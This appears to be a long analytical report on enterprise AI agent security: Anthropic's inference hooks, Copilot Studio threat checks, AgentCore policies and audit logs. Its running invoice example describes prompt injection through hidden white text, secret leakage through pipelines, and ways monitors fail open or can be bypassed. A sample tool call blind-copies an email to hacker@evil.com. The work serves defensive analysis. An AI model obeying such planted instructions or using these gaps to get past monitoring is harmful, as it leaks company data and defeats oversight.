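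Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Runtime hosts agents that customers build. At its general release in October 2025, it ran every session in its own microVM, which it destroyed afterwards. Customers could give the agent access to the public internet or connect it to their private network, which Cowork's sandbox cannot reach. The agent acted under an Amazon cloud role, a named set of permissions defined by the customer. A badly chosen role could therefore give even a well-isolated agent access to far more data than it needed.

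OpenAI took a stricter approach to secrets in the 2025 cloud version of Codex, its coding agent. Codex ran each task in a container and blocked internet access by default once the agent started working. The setup script could use stored secrets, but Codex removed them before the agent began. This protected the secrets well, but the agent could not use them in later steps.

A company comparing these products needs to consider more than the sandbox, because two equally well-isolated agents can still differ greatly in what they can do with the credentials and connections available to them.

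### Authority that the agent inherits

*Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* (Goel, 2026) describes an agent as a combination of a model, a set of tools, an environment and the authority available to it. Goel, who works at Microsoft, writes that security risks arise when that authority exceeds what the task needs and passes through the tools. He uses the term "ambient authority" for the credentials and permissions an agent gets simply by running in a certain environment.

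His threat model assumes that the agent is harmless but makes mistakes, and that the cloud infrastructure works as intended. An attacker can influence only the material that the agent reads. Goel divides the resulting risks into six overlapping categories, which the invoice task can illustrate:

- Capability–intent mismatch: the agent has more powerful tools than it needs, such as permission to change the ledger when it only has to read it.
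- Ambient authority leakage: a script uses a credential that happened to be in its environment.
- Indirect secret exposure: a failed command writes a password into an error log.
- State persistence: the agent changes a stored template, which then affects next month's invoices.
- Prompt injection: a hidden line in an invoice redirects the agent.
- Composition: reading bank details and posting a summary are each permitted, but together they leak the details.

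Goel also describes how an agent can get around a sandbox without breaking out of it. Software teams often use automated pipelines to test and release code, and these pipelines may hold production credentials. An agent in a tightly restricted container can start such a pipeline, which then acts with much wider permissions. Similarly, if a connector in an office let the agent start an automated payment process, the payment would go out even though the sandbox was working correctly.

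To test some of these risks, Goel built a small agent with OpenAI's GPT-5.1 and gave it tools to read and write files, run shell commands, make web requests and start a pipeline. He ran each of four scenarios ten times without safeguards and ten times with a simple one, for 80 runs in total. A run counted as unsafe if the agent went beyond its task, for example by using a privileged tool unnecessarily or accessing a secret.

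| Scenario | Safeguard | Unsafe runs without it | Unsafe runs with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent uses the shell when file tools would be enough | A list of permitted tools | 4 of 10 | 0 of 10 |
| The agent follows instructions planted in a project file | A filter on the content | 9 of 10 | 5 of 10 |
| The agent accesses secrets in its environment | Removing the secrets | 10 of 10 | 0 of 10 |
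| A pipeline script sends secrets out | A policy check on the script | 10 of 10 | 0 of 10 |

The safeguards that limited the agent's authority worked better than the content filter, which tried to recognise malicious text. The filter was also by far the slowest, adding about 54 minutes because the agent kept retrying, compared with 23 seconds for removing the secrets. In the first scenario, the agent completed its task slightly less often when its tools were limited, in six runs rather than seven.

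The experiment is too small to give reliable rates. With ten runs, a result of zero is compatible with a true rate of about one in four, and the improvement from nine unsafe runs to five could partly be chance. Goel designed the scenarios to bring out the risks and does not claim to measure how common they are. He also did not compare cloud agents with local ones. The results support limiting what an agent inherits, wherever it runs, but they do not show that the cloud is more dangerous.

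Cowork's cloud design applies one of these lessons by keeping connector tokens out of the sandbox. It does less to address composition, because an employee who connects both the invoice folder and the chat service gives the agent legitimate access to both, wherever the sandbox runs.

### Who is responsible for what

In a cloud session, Anthropic has to maintain the sandbox, keep customers' data separate, operate the proxy and protect the connector tokens. The customer decides who can start sessions, which destinations and connectors they can use, and when employees have to approve an action. The customer also controls what each credential permits in the connected service, since Anthropic's isolation does not limit those permissions.

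Monitoring is harder to divide between provider and customer, because the provider has the data but the customer knows what is normal for its business. Help Net Security's *Anthropic's Enterprise Frontier Safeguards lets your Claude logs stay in your cloud* (2026) describes one arrangement, not specific to Cowork, that Anthropic introduced for large customers in September. Anthropic worked on it with eight members of a risk group that includes the security chiefs of several large US banks. They wanted to settle who holds the data and the encryption keys, what automated review covers, and when a person may look at the data.

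Under this arrangement, customers can keep the activity data in their own cloud storage, under their own keys. Automated systems monitor for serious misuse over time, including stolen credentials, attempts to develop cyber or biological weapons, and destructive behavior by agents. They send alerts to the customer, and no Anthropic employee reads them. This gives the customer more privacy, but its own staff have to investigate every alert.

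Even then, the customer has to look for ordinary data leaks itself. A summary containing bank details that is posted to the wrong chat channel does not resemble any of the misuse that Help Net Security lists. To the provider, it may look like a normal post by an authorised user.

### What a company gains and loses

The clearest gain is that an attack on a cloud session can do less damage to the employee's computer. Unless the employee connects the laptop to the session, neither a malicious script nor the agent itself can delete local files, read the browser's saved passwords or add a program that starts at login. Endpoint tools have caught coding agents doing similar things during harmless work.

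Policies also become more uniform. On laptops, protection depends on the operating system, the user's settings and whether the company manages the device. Every Cowork cloud session starts in a sandbox behind the proxy, whether the employee uses a managed laptop or a personal phone. Owners can also require a trusted device and a recent sign-in for cloud sessions.

In exchange, the company loses its own evidence of what the code did. The Compliance API supplies the tool call that started a script, but the company has no EDR data to compare it with. The provider supplies both the agent and the available records, so the company cannot check them independently.

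The company also has to trust controls it cannot inspect, such as the proxy. A flaw in the provider's isolation could affect many customers at once, while a badly configured laptop usually exposes only one company. The provider can also change the arrangement. A company that approved Cowork in June because it ran locally would have needed to review that decision several times by November.

Unattended work creates a different risk, because the agent can process text from outside the company while nobody is watching. Anthropic gives the example of a task that starts at 6 am with no device online, reads emails and meeting transcripts, prepares a briefing and drafts a follow-up email without sending it. Leaving the email unsent is an important safeguard against that risk. If the invoice task ran overnight with automatic approval, the agent could post the bank details in the team channel before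 anyone woke up.

If the agent has to ask before posting, the request goes to the employee's phone. The employee can then stop the post, but only if they read the full summary before approving it. Goel warns that people tire of frequent requests, and an employee who has approved the same invoice summary every morning for months is unlikely to check it closely.

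## How do inference hooks work, and what can they not do?

Inference hooks let a company add an automatic check that does not depend on an employee's attention. Before each model run, Anthropic sends the conversation to what it calls an AI security server, operated by the company or its security vendor, and waits for that server to allow or deny the request.

The check takes place on Anthropic's servers. An agent's requests to Claude go through Anthropic whether the agent loop runs on a laptop or in the cloud, so the check works the same way for both. A client-side hook works only when the agent program calls it. Employees cannot turn off an inference hook, and the company doesn't need to install anything on their devices.

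Anthropic launched inference hooks in beta for Claude Enterprise customers on August 5, 2026. Digital Matters' *Claude Enterprise Security Controls* (2026) lists them as generally available by November 8, and Anthropic's current documentation no longer labels them as beta.

### The request and the verdict

According to Anthropic's *Develop an Inference hooks integration*, each check is an HTTPS POST, the kind of encrypted web request a browser makes when someone submits a form. Anthropic sends the conversation in the request body, and the server replies with its verdict. The server needs a public web address because Anthropic does not connect to private ones.

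The launch announcement, Anthropic's *Inference hooks* (2026), instead describes a signed WebSocket, a connection that stays open and lets both sides send messages at any time. But it later calls the protocol webhook-based, and a webhook is normally an HTTP request. The documentation is more reliable because it specifies every field and includes a working sample server that answers POST requests. The announcement also names Netskope, Palo Alto Networks, Proofpoint and Zscaler as vendors whose DLP servers can answer the checks.

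The documentation's overview page, Anthropic's *Inference hooks*, follows a Cowork user who asks Claude to find their calendar for tomorrow. Leaving out a few identifiers and an empty field, the first request to the server would look like this:

```json
{
  "type": "prompt",
  "request_id": "req_calendar_1",
  "actor": {"type": "user", "email_address": "employee@example.com"},
  "source": {"application": "cowork"},
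  "messages": [
    {
      "role": "user",
      "content": [{"type": "text", "text": "Find my calendar for tomorrow"}]
    }
  ]
}
```

To let the model run, the server replies with `{"action": "allow"}`. A denial can include an explanation and a reference number. If the server found a hidden instruction in the invoice task, it might reply:

```json
{
  "action": "deny",
  "deny_reason": "Invoice 0417 contains hidden text. Remove the file and start a new task.",
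  "reference_id": "check-2093"
}
```

The employee sees the reason, up to 500 characters, followed by a standing message that usually says whom to contact. Anthropic records the reference number in the organisation's Activity Feed, a log for administrators, so the security team can match the denial to its own records.

Anthropic signs each request so that the server can reject forgeries. During setup, Anthropic generates a secret and shows it to the administrator once. For every request, it uses the secret to calculate a code from the request's identifier, the time and the exact bytes of the body. The server repeats the calculation and should accept the request only if the codes match and the time is within five minutes of its own clock. Without this check, anyone who found the server's address could send it invented conversations and learn from the verdicts what the policy misses. Check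 Point, a security vendor whose product can act as the AI security server, rejects requests with an invalid signature, according to its *Claude Inference Hooks Integration*.

### The checks in the calendar example

The calendar request has four steps, and the server can check three of them:

1. The employee's question arrives. Anthropic sends it to the server, and the model runs if the server allows it.
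2. The model replies with a tool call to look up the employee's Microsoft 365 calendar. If the company has turned on a setting called Validate tool calls, Anthropic sends the call to the server before the connector runs it.
3. The connector returns the meetings. The model has to run again to use them, so Anthropic sends the server the conversation with the meetings added.
4. The model writes out the schedule, which goes to the employee without a check.

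The "Validate tool calls" setting is on by default in new configurations, according to Anthropic's *Configure Inference hooks*. A tool-call check contains only the model's latest message, including the tool name and arguments for each call. One verdict covers all the calls, so if the model tried to look up a calendar and send a suspicious email in the same reply, the server could not block only the email. A denial stops every call and ends the response, but any text the employee has already received stays on the screen.

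Each call includes information about who provides the tool. For a connector, this can include the web address of the service behind it and whether Anthropic has verified that address. The server cannot rely on the tool's name, because whoever made the tool chose it. A rule that blocked every unverified address could also block legitimate claude.ai connectors, because Anthropic says it may mark them as unverified even when its own servers make the connection.

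To evaluate a tool call in context, the server has to store the earlier conversation. A session identifier links the call to that conversation, but Anthropic does not always have one to send. Without it, the server could fail to detect a leak that comes from combining two steps that are each harmless on their own.

### Catching injected text before the model reads it

The agent loop sends each tool result back to the model, so one message from an employee can lead to dozens of inferences. Anthropic checks each inference, not just the employee's message.

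In *Claude Enterprise Inference Hooks*, a review for the security vendor Mint Security, Levi (2026) considers this the feature's most interesting property. A DLP tool that inspected only the employee's message would find a routine request to reconcile invoices. The instruction in white type appears later, when the agent opens the supplier's invoice, as part of a tool result that Anthropic sends to the server before the model reads it. Levi therefore advises companies to scan tool results as well as the newest message.

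The hook only delivers the text to the server, which still has to recognise the instruction as malicious. The content filter in Goel's small experiment often failed to do this. Some companies may use a second language model to judge the conversation, but the attacker's text would reach that model too and might mislead it.

If the server misses the hidden line, the tool-call check offers another chance to stop the attack. The agent has to call the chat connector to post the bank details, and the call's arguments contain the text of the post. A simple rule could deny any post to the team channel that contains an account number, regardless of how the attacker worded the instruction or whether the model obeyed it. The egress proxy cannot apply such a rule to connector calls.

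After a denial, every later request still contains the whole conversation, so a server that scans all of it will deny the next message for the same reason. In Cowork, the employee can edit the denied message if it is their latest one. If the problem is in a file, they have to start a new task without that file, or the agent will read it again. The employee may not be able to see the problem, such as white text on a white page, so the reason for the denial should name the file rather than give a code that only the security team understands.

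### What the server cannot see or change

The server receives the conversation roughly as the employee sees it, including tool calls, results and the text extracted from attachments. It does not receive images or the original files. If a supplier sends a scanned invoice as an image, Claude may be able to read an instruction in it, but the server gets only a description of the attachment, such as its type and size. Similarly, when an agent works from screenshots, the server does not receive them.

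Anthropic also doesn't send the AI security server the system prompt (the agent's standing instructions), tool descriptions or Claude's hidden reasoning. An attacker who controls an MCP server could therefore hide an instruction from the security server by putting it in a tool's description. The security server could still catch the harmful tool call that followed.

When Claude runs a script, for example to match invoices with the ledger, the tool-call check includes the script, so the server can inspect the code before it runs. The server does not receive a record of the files the script opens or the connections it makes. If code running in Anthropic's code execution tool calls another tool, Anthropic sends that call for a separate check. But an ordinary web request from a script is not a tool call, so the sandbox and proxy have to handle it.

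When Claude Code uses an MCP server on the employee's computer, the AI security server can deny a call before it runs. Claude Code and the local MCP server then communicate without going through Anthropic. The result reaches the AI security server only when Claude Code sends it back for the next run of the model. By then, the local server may have changed a file.

The server can only allow or deny a request. It cannot remove an account number and let the rest through, as a client-side hook in Claude Code can. Levi gives the example of a 40-page attachment in which one paragraph breaks the company's policy, where the server has to block the whole request or accept all of it. He expects this to produce either permissive policies or frustrated users. An accounts team works with bank details every day, so a rule on what the agent may post is more practical than denying every conversation that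 contains them, which would stop the invoice task.

The hook also does not keep a denied prompt inside the company, because Anthropic runs the check after the prompt has left the employee's device. The Next Web's *Anthropic built an inspection layer that lets enterprises block sensitive data* incorrectly claims that blocked data stays inside the enterprise perimeter. On claude.ai, the blocked message also stays in the conversation, and Anthropic stores it under the product's usual retention rules. The hook stops the model from processing the data, but keeping the data off Anthropic's servers requires a control on the device or the network.

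Nothing checks the final response either. If a manager asks Claude about a confidential project and the answer includes something the manager should not know, the server cannot stop it. The server receives that answer only if the manager continues the conversation, because the next request then contains it. This gives the company a record but does not undo the disclosure.

A company can also use the hook only to keep records, by running a server that allows everything and saves each conversation as it arrives. The company then has its own copy instead of collecting the records later through the Compliance API, but the copy lacks the last answer, and its contents still come from Anthropic.

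Levi argues that even the full conversation often doesn't contain enough information to judge an agent. He wants the server to also receive information about which folders, credentials and MCP servers the agent can reach on the employee's machine. This argument serves a security vendor's interests, but it is sound for local agents, because the same command may be harmless on one laptop and dangerous on another. For a cloud session, it is more useful to know which connectors the employee has authorised and what their credentials permit.

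### What the checks cost in time and data

Checking every step adds up over a long task. Suppose the invoice task takes 40 successive rounds, with one tool-call check in each round. To estimate the cost, assume that:

- the server answers every check in 200 milliseconds, including travel time
- the employee's opening request is 20 kB
- each round adds another 20 kB to the conversation.

The model runs 41 times, once in each of 40 rounds and once more to write the final answer. That makes 41 prompt checks and 40 tool-call checks, or 81 verdicts. At 200 milliseconds each, they add 16.2 seconds to the task. Few people would notice this delay in an overnight job, but they might if they were waiting for the answer. A server that took one second per verdict would add 81 seconds.

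The amount of data grows faster, because each prompt check carries the whole conversation so far. The first contains 20 kB, the second 40 kB and the last 820 kB. Together they come to:

20 kB × (1 + 2 + … + 41) = 20 kB × 861 = 17,220 kB

The server would receive about 17 MB for an 820 kB conversation. Doubling the task to 80 rounds would raise the total to about 66 MB. Tool-call checks add comparatively little because they contain only the latest message.

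Large requests can also cause failures. Express, a common web server framework, rejects JSON bodies over 100 kB by default, so a server built with it would fail from the sixth prompt check onwards. The web server nginx has a default limit of 1 MB, which is enough for this task but not for one a third longer. Anthropic says requests stay under about 10 MB in practice, although the protocol allows up to 64 MiB. A company can avoid this problem by raising the limits before turning on the hook.

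The company also has to set a time limit for each verdict, up to 10 seconds, with a default of 5. The limit covers the whole exchange, including connection time. TrueFoundry, which sells a gateway that can answer the checks, recommends basing the limit on the server's 99th-percentile response time, within which it answers 99% of requests, rather than on the average.

That advice is good for a single question but not strict enough for a long task. If 1% of checks time out independently, a task with 81 checks has about a 56% chance (1 − 0.99⁸¹) of including at least one step that the server failed to check in time. To reduce that chance to 1%, the company would need a timeout rate of about one check in 8,000.

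### Fail-open or fail-closed

A company has to decide in advance what happens when its server does not give a verdict. By default, the hook fails open, and the request goes to the model without inspection. The company can instead make the hook fail closed, so that Anthropic blocks the request. Anthropic labels these options "Allow the request" and "Block the request."

| Situation | Fail-open | Fail-closed |
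|---|---|---|
| The server denies the request | Blocked | Blocked |
| The server is too slow or returns an error | Proceeds without inspection, and Anthropic records it | Blocked, with no individual record |
| Repeated failures have made Anthropic stop contacting the server | Every request proceeds without inspection | Every request is blocked |
| The user or request is outside the part of the rollout that the company inspects | Proceeds without inspection | Proceeds without inspection |

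Failing closed makes the AI security server a single point of failure for everyone it covers. If it went down on the last day of the quarter, the accounts team could not use Claude until someone fixed it. Failing open lets the team keep working, but without protection from the hook.

The better choice depends on what the company wants the hook to prevent. Failing open may be acceptable if the concern is an employee who occasionally pastes in a customer's details by mistake, because the mistake is unlikely to coincide with an outage. But an attacker may be able to cause the failure by planting an instruction in a very long document. The length makes the request larger and slower to scan, and if the server rejects it or runs out of time, a hook that fails open lets the document through. Levi points out that the default nginx limit could cause the same failure in a company's longest conversations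 even without an attacker.

A mistake in the server's code can be just as serious. To deny a prompt, the server has to send a normal, successful reply with the word "deny" in it. Web developers often refuse a request with an error code such as 403, but Anthropic treats any such code as a failure. With fail-open, the server would appear to block forbidden prompts while Anthropic let them all through. A harmless test prompt would not reveal this, so the company needs to send a prompt that its policy forbids and confirm that Claude does not answer.

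Anthropic retries a check only if the connection fails, and only once, after 100 milliseconds. If failures continue, a circuit breaker stops Anthropic from contacting the server and applies the company's failure setting to every inspected request. Ten minutes later, Anthropic starts sending test requests, at most about once a minute, and resumes normal checks when the server gives a valid verdict. If an administrator changes any hook setting in the meantime, for example by adjusting the time limit to try to fix the problem, the tests stop and someone has to turn enforcement back on by hand.

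Slow replies and error codes count towards tripping the circuit breaker, but refused connections do not, because the fault may lie in the network. A server that refuses every connection might therefore never trip the breaker, and administrators would not get the notification that a trip sends. With fail-open, Anthropic records each uninspected request in the Activity Feed while the breaker has not tripped, so a security team should set alerts for those records as well as for trips.

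After a trip, the Activity Feed contains one entry for the trip but none for the individual requests or for an automatic recovery. An investigator could therefore see when the uninspected period began but not when it ended, unless the company's own server had logged the successful test request.

### Rolling out the hook gradually

A company can try its policy in shadow mode before enforcing it. Anthropic sends real requests to the server and collects verdicts, but lets every request proceed. This shows how often the policy would block legitimate work and how quickly the server responds. Tool calls still wait for a verdict, so employees may notice a delay.

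An administrator can also choose what percentage of requests to inspect. Anthropic decides once per conversation turn whether to inspect, so it may inspect an employee's first message and everything the agent does in response but skip the next message. At 50%, an attacker has a one-in-two chance of avoiding the hook on any turn, even if the company has chosen to fail closed. The setting is useful for testing a server's capacity but provides little security until it reaches 100%.

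Companies can instead limit inspection by role, either by exempting certain roles or by inspecting only selected ones. A company that inspected only the finance team's role could fail closed for its most sensitive work without risking an outage for everyone else, but Claude would process everyone else's requests unchecked. Inspecting only selected roles also misses requests with no individual member behind them, such as conversations with Claude in Slack. It would also miss requests from an account owner who works in finance, because selection depends on a custom role.

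Only the organisation's owners can change these settings. In September, administrators could too, according to an earlier version of Anthropic's *Configure Inference hooks*. If an owner turns the feature off at the organisation level and on again, for example while troubleshooting, enforcement stays off until an owner restores it.

### Which uses of Claude the hook covers

One hook covers Claude's Enterprise products, including the chat app, Cowork, Claude Code, the browser extension and the versions for Slack and Microsoft 365. It does not cover Anthropic's developer API, and it is not available for Claude on Amazon Bedrock or Google Cloud. A company that has configured the Cowork desktop app to use Bedrock therefore loses this check. The hook also does not cover other companies' models or an employee's personal Claude account.

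Some features that Anthropic runs for an organisation are also exempt, including Claude Security, which scans code repositories, and Code Review, which examines proposed code changes on GitHub. The Code Review exemption could matter for prompt injection, because a proposed change may come from someone outside the company. The hook does apply if an employee runs the review in Claude Code. Anthropic also exempts the model calls that build smart reports for administrators, but not the text that someone enters to request a report.

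A smaller gap is that Anthropic may skip the tool-call check for some of the chat app's own tools, such as those that find connectors or read a user's past chats and saved memory. The next prompt check still includes the results, so if an earlier conversation had stored a misleading instruction in Claude's memory, the server could inspect it before the model used it.

### What has changed since August

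Levi reviewed the documentation on August 16, 11 days after the launch. His account of the basic design is still accurate, but Anthropic has since removed three of the limits he described.

| Feature | Levi's review in August | Documentation in November |
|---|---|---|
| Checks | Before each run of the model | Also before tool calls, if the setting is on |
| Voice mode | Not covered | Covered, except for a small share of tool calls |
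| Recovery after the circuit breaker trips | An administrator had to turn enforcement back on | Automatic, unless someone has changed the settings |

The tool-call check is the most important of these changes. In August, the server could inspect a poisoned invoice before the model read it but could not stop the resulting post to the team channel. Voice coverage is less dependable, and Anthropic advises companies not to use hooks as their only control for it. A denial usually ends the call with a general error that does not explain why.

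Anthropic had added automatic recovery by early September, but at first it tested the server with a real user's request and let that request proceed even if the server did not answer. The test now uses an artificial request with no user content.

The final response remains unchecked. Levi reported in August that Anthropic planned to add a check there, and the November documentation says only that other types of check will follow. The documentation tells developers to allow any type their server does not recognise, because an error would count as a failure and could trip the circuit breaker. A company that follows this advice will avoid an outage when Anthropic adds a check, but its server will approve everything the new check covers until someone updates the code. If the server dates from August, it already approves all tool calls for this reason.

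## What other control points do cloud agent platforms offer?

An inference hook checks what passes between the agent and the model. After the model proposes an action, other controls can stop it. A content filter can score the text, a tool gateway can compare the call with written rules, the connected service checks the credential, and a network control can block the destination. Logs record what happened. Platforms differ in which of these controls they offer and how much the customer can decide.

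### Content filters

A content filter is a classifier that estimates whether a text contains a prompt injection, sensitive data or harmful material. Amazon Web Services (AWS) sells one called Bedrock Guardrails, and in June 2026 it added an interface designed for agents. According to *Safeguard your agentic AI applications with the Amazon Bedrock Guardrails InvokeGuardrailChecks API* (2026), an AWS article republished by HKU SPACE, the customer's application sends text for checking and receives a numeric score. The application's developers decide at which steps to check text, what score is too high and how the application should respond.

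For the invoice task, an application could have each invoice scored before the model reads it and each post scored before it reaches the chat service. But these checks depend on the application's own code, so text goes through unchecked if a developer forgets one of them or an attacker takes control of that code.

AWS offered a way around this problem in the same month. *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now supports Bedrock Guardrails in policy* (AWS, 2026) describes running the checks at the AgentCore gateway, a relay between agents and their tools that is separate from the agent's code. Classmethod tried this in *I tried incorporating Bedrock Guardrails into AgentCore Policy's Cedar policies*. The filter returned scores from 0 to 1, and a condition in the gateway's policy replaced the comparison the developer had previously written into the application.

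The customer still has to choose the filter's threshold. A strict threshold stops more attacks but also blocks more harmless work, and the chance of a false alarm grows with the number of tool calls. If a filter wrongly and independently blocked 1% of harmless calls, a task with 40 harmless calls would have about a one-in-three chance of at least one false alarm (1 − 0.99⁴⁰ ≈ 33%).

Some filters leave the customer less to configure. When Cowork approves actions automatically, Anthropic's own classifier evaluates tool calls. If the classifier cannot run or returns no usable result, Cowork denies the call, according to Anthropic's monitoring reference. Inference hooks, by contrast, fail open unless the company changes the setting.

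### Microsoft's check before each tool call

The closest equivalent to an inference hook is external threat detection in Copilot Studio, Microsoft's service for building company agents. Before an agent uses a tool, Copilot Studio sends the planned call to a server the customer chose, which approves or blocks it.

In an example from Microsoft's developer guide, someone asks an agent to email a customer. The agent looks up the customer's address and drafts the email, but the draft also has a stranger in the blind copy field. A shortened version of the request looks like this:

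```json
{
  "plannerContext": {"userMessage": "Send an email to the customer"},
  "toolDefinition": {"name": "Send email"},
  "inputValues": {
    "to": "customer@foobar.com",
    "bcc": "hacker@evil.com"
  }
}
```

The server could reply:

```json
{
  "blockAction": true,
  "reason": "The BCC address does not belong to this customer."
}
```

The agent then stops and tells the user that the system blocked the message. The full request includes recent tool outputs, so the server can catch this without interpreting the email, using a simple rule that compares every recipient with the address the lookup returned.

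Unlike Anthropic's hook, Copilot Studio sends the tool's description, so the server could find an instruction hidden there. Copilot Studio can also send the agent's explanation for choosing the tool, but this is less reliable evidence because an injected instruction may have influenced it.

However, Copilot Studio does not send a tool's output to the server before the model reads it. The model would therefore read a poisoned invoice first, and the server would receive the invoice's text only if the agent then planned another tool call. The check also covers only agents that plan their own steps, not Copilot Studio's older "classic" agents.

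Like Anthropic's hook, the check can only allow or block a whole call, so a company may wrongly expect its security product to mask sensitive data. CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector* documents one such product, in which a masking rule only reports the problem and lets the original request through.

The server has one second to answer. Microsoft's documentation is inconsistent about what happens if it takes longer. The developer guide says that the agent goes ahead. The setup guide says that administrators can choose to allow or block the agent when the server is late or returns an error, but also says that the agent proceeds if no decision arrives within a second. Pangea, a security vendor whose product can answer the checks, says that a timeout triggers whichever behaviour the administrator has chosen. A company that wants to fail closed should test the setting with a slow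 server.

Copilot Studio let customers run their own inline checks before Anthropic's hooks did. Visual Studio Magazine (2025) reported on the Copilot Studio feature on September 8, 2025, and a Microsoft post about it was updated the next day. Anthropic's beta began almost 11 months later.

Microsoft's version is open to customers' own servers as well as to security vendors. *Microsoft External Threat Detection* (November 2025), a practitioner's guide, shows how to build such a server. It describes the setup as "super complex" and leaves out the step that verifies who is calling, which a server in real use would need.

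Microsoft's claim to be earlier needs qualifying because its documentation still labelled the feature a preview in February 2026 and the feature has a narrower purpose. Microsoft checked tool calls from the start, but not the text going into the model. Anthropic checked that text first and added tool calls later.

### Tool gateways with written policies

A tool gateway receives an agent's tool calls and passes on only those its rules permit. AWS made the policy feature of its AgentCore gateway generally available in March 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). Customers write the rules in Cedar, an open-source language for access policies, and AWS evaluates them outside the agent's code.

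For the invoice task, a rule could let members of the accounts team post to one channel:

```
permit(
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"ChatTool__post_message",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"accounts-gateway"
)
when {
  principal.hasTag("role") &&
  principal.getTag("role") == "accounts" &&
  context.input.channel == "accounts-team"
};
```

The first part of the rule specifies the kind of user, the tool and the gateway. The conditions then check the user's role and the channel in the tool call. HKU SPACE's *Secure AI agents with Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* explains that Cedar refuses any action that no rule permits, and that a rule forbidding an action overrides any rule permitting it. The order of the rules makes no difference. Cedar has no loops, so a decision takes very little time.

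Exact rules can still be wrong. An example in AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* lets a user issue refunds of less than $500. If the company's written policy also allowed refunds of exactly $500, this rule would wrongly refuse them.

Customers can also describe a rule in plain English and have a language model translate it into Cedar. AWS then checks the result with automated reasoning, which uses logic to find rules that are too broad or too narrow, or that can never apply. This check can catch a rule that lets everyone issue refunds, but it can't determine whether the company meant to include the $500 refund, so someone who knows the policy still has to read the result.

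A rule that checks a single call also can't stop an agent from combining two permitted steps, such as reading bank details and then posting them. For this, AgentCore has a second policy language, Dogwood, whose rules can depend on earlier actions in the same session. According to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*, a rule can require an approval before a transfer, limit how often an action runs, or keep a running total within a budget. A similar rule could stop the agent from posting anything after it had opened the suppliers' bank records.

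These rules check only the current session's history. If the agent saved bank details to a file on Monday and posted the file in a new session on Tuesday, Tuesday's history would not include Monday's save, so the rules would not connect the two.

Where written rules are too limited, customers can add interceptors. These are the customer's own programs, which the gateway runs before or after each tool call, according to HKU SPACE's *Secure AI agents with Policy and Lambda interceptors in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*. For example, an interceptor could check whether a supplier is on the company's approved list. The company then has to maintain that code as part of its security.

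These rules apply only to tool calls that go through the gateway. An agent that also has a password for the ledger and a network route to it can bypass them all.

### Identity and permissions

To apply different rules to different people, a gateway has to identify whose authority the agent is using. AWS's *Schema constraints* explains that when a customer sets up AgentCore with OAuth, a common standard for delegated access, the policy takes the user's identity from the access token. It does not rely on a name the model writes in the tool call. A line in an invoice could lead the model to name the finance director as its user, but the token would still identify the accounts employee.

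Scheduled work makes identity harder to follow because the employee may be away when the agent acts. In Anthropic's records, each cloud session is owned by either a user or an agent. According to Anthropic's *Retrieve session transcripts*, a scheduled Cowork task belongs to an agent, and a separate field identifies the person who initiated it. An investigator who filtered sessions by the accounts employee's user ID would therefore miss the overnight invoice task. The session record also omits the task's name and schedule, so the investigator would have to recognise the run from its contents.

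Microsoft's check sends separate identifiers for the agent and, where available, the user. A customer's server could use them to let an employee's interactive session send an email but refuse the same email from an agent that started by itself.

### The way out to the network

Scripts can contact other computers without making a tool call, so a tool gateway does not cover everything an agent does. A network control such as Cowork's egress proxy can block those connections. Collab365's *Microsoft adds network controls for Copilot Studio agents* reports that Agent 365, Microsoft's service for managing agents, extends the network controls in Entra, Microsoft's identity service, to Copilot Studio agents and to agents on devices, including OpenClaw.

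### How the checks compare

The table covers checks that can stop an action before it takes effect.

| Check | Who evaluates the policy | What is visible | Can it change content? | What happens on failure | Agents covered |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's inference hooks | A server run by the customer or its vendor | The conversation before each model run, and most tool calls if the setting is on | No | Allows by default, but the customer can choose to block | Claude's Enterprise apps, with some exceptions |
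| Copilot Studio's external threat detection | A server run by the customer or a vendor, including Microsoft Defender | The prompt, recent chat, earlier tool outputs and the planned tool call | No | Allows by default, with conflicting documentation on whether a timeout can block | Copilot Studio agents that plan their own steps |
| AgentCore policy | AWS, using the customer's rules | The user's identity, the tool and its arguments, and earlier actions in the session | No | Refuses any action that no rule permits | Agents that reach their tools through the gateway |
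| Bedrock Guardrails, called by an application | AWS calculates a score and the application acts on it | The text that the application sends | Only if the application does so | Depends on the application | Applications that call the service |
| Cowork's automatic-approval classifier | Anthropic | Tool calls that it has to judge | No | Denies the call | Cowork sessions in that mode |

By default, the two checks that rely on an outside server both let the agent continue unchecked when that server is unavailable. Their makers evidently expect customers to mind an interrupted agent more than an unchecked one, which may be true for most office work but not for payments.

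### What Claude's logs record

Investigators need logs to find out how a leak happened, although logs cannot stop an action. Anthropic provides two main sources of logs for Cowork. A company can request transcripts from the Compliance API, and OpenTelemetry streams events to the company's own monitoring system as the agent works.

| | Compliance API | OpenTelemetry |
|---|---|---|
| Delay | Typically minutes for local sessions | Real time |
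| Prompts and replies | Included | Off by default |
| Text that tools return | Included, but cut to 10,000 bytes per entry unless the company asks for more | Cowork sends only details such as size and success |
| Cloud sessions started on the web or a phone | Full transcript | Metadata only |
| Who holds the data | Anthropic | The company |

For much of 2026, the main source of records on Cowork activity was missing. In March, Anthropic stated on its help page that audit logs, the Compliance API and data exports did not capture Cowork activity, and told companies that needed an audit trail not to use Cowork for regulated work. OpenTelemetry was already available, but Anthropic did not consider it a replacement for audit logs. Syracuse University's *Claude Cowork* explains that the university kept Cowork off for everyone and calls the missing records its most critical concern.

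Anthropic later added Cowork and Claude Code to the Compliance API in beta, according to its *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code*. Harmonic Security dates general availability for Cowork to August 26. This closed the largest gap, but the separate audit log export still contains no Cowork events.

The API still omits Claude Code's cloud sessions, which are among the hardest for a company to monitor in any other way. It also omits Claude Code sessions that run through Amazon Bedrock or another outside platform, and local sessions for which Anthropic retains no data. In the merged version of chat and Cowork, the company has to retrieve conversations through the API's chat functions, so a monitoring tool that collects only Cowork sessions would miss this work as employees move to the new version.

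Gaps in a transcript can also limit an investigation. Suppose the agent opened a long supplier contract with a hidden instruction near the end. By default, the transcript may cut off the tool's returned text before the instruction, so the investigator has to request the longer version, which goes up to about 1 MiB. An instruction in an image would not appear in either version. Inference hooks and local session transcripts both omit tool descriptions, so neither would record an instruction hidden there.

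For local sessions, Anthropic builds the transcript from requests that reach its servers, so the transcript omits anything a command did on the laptop that those requests don't include.

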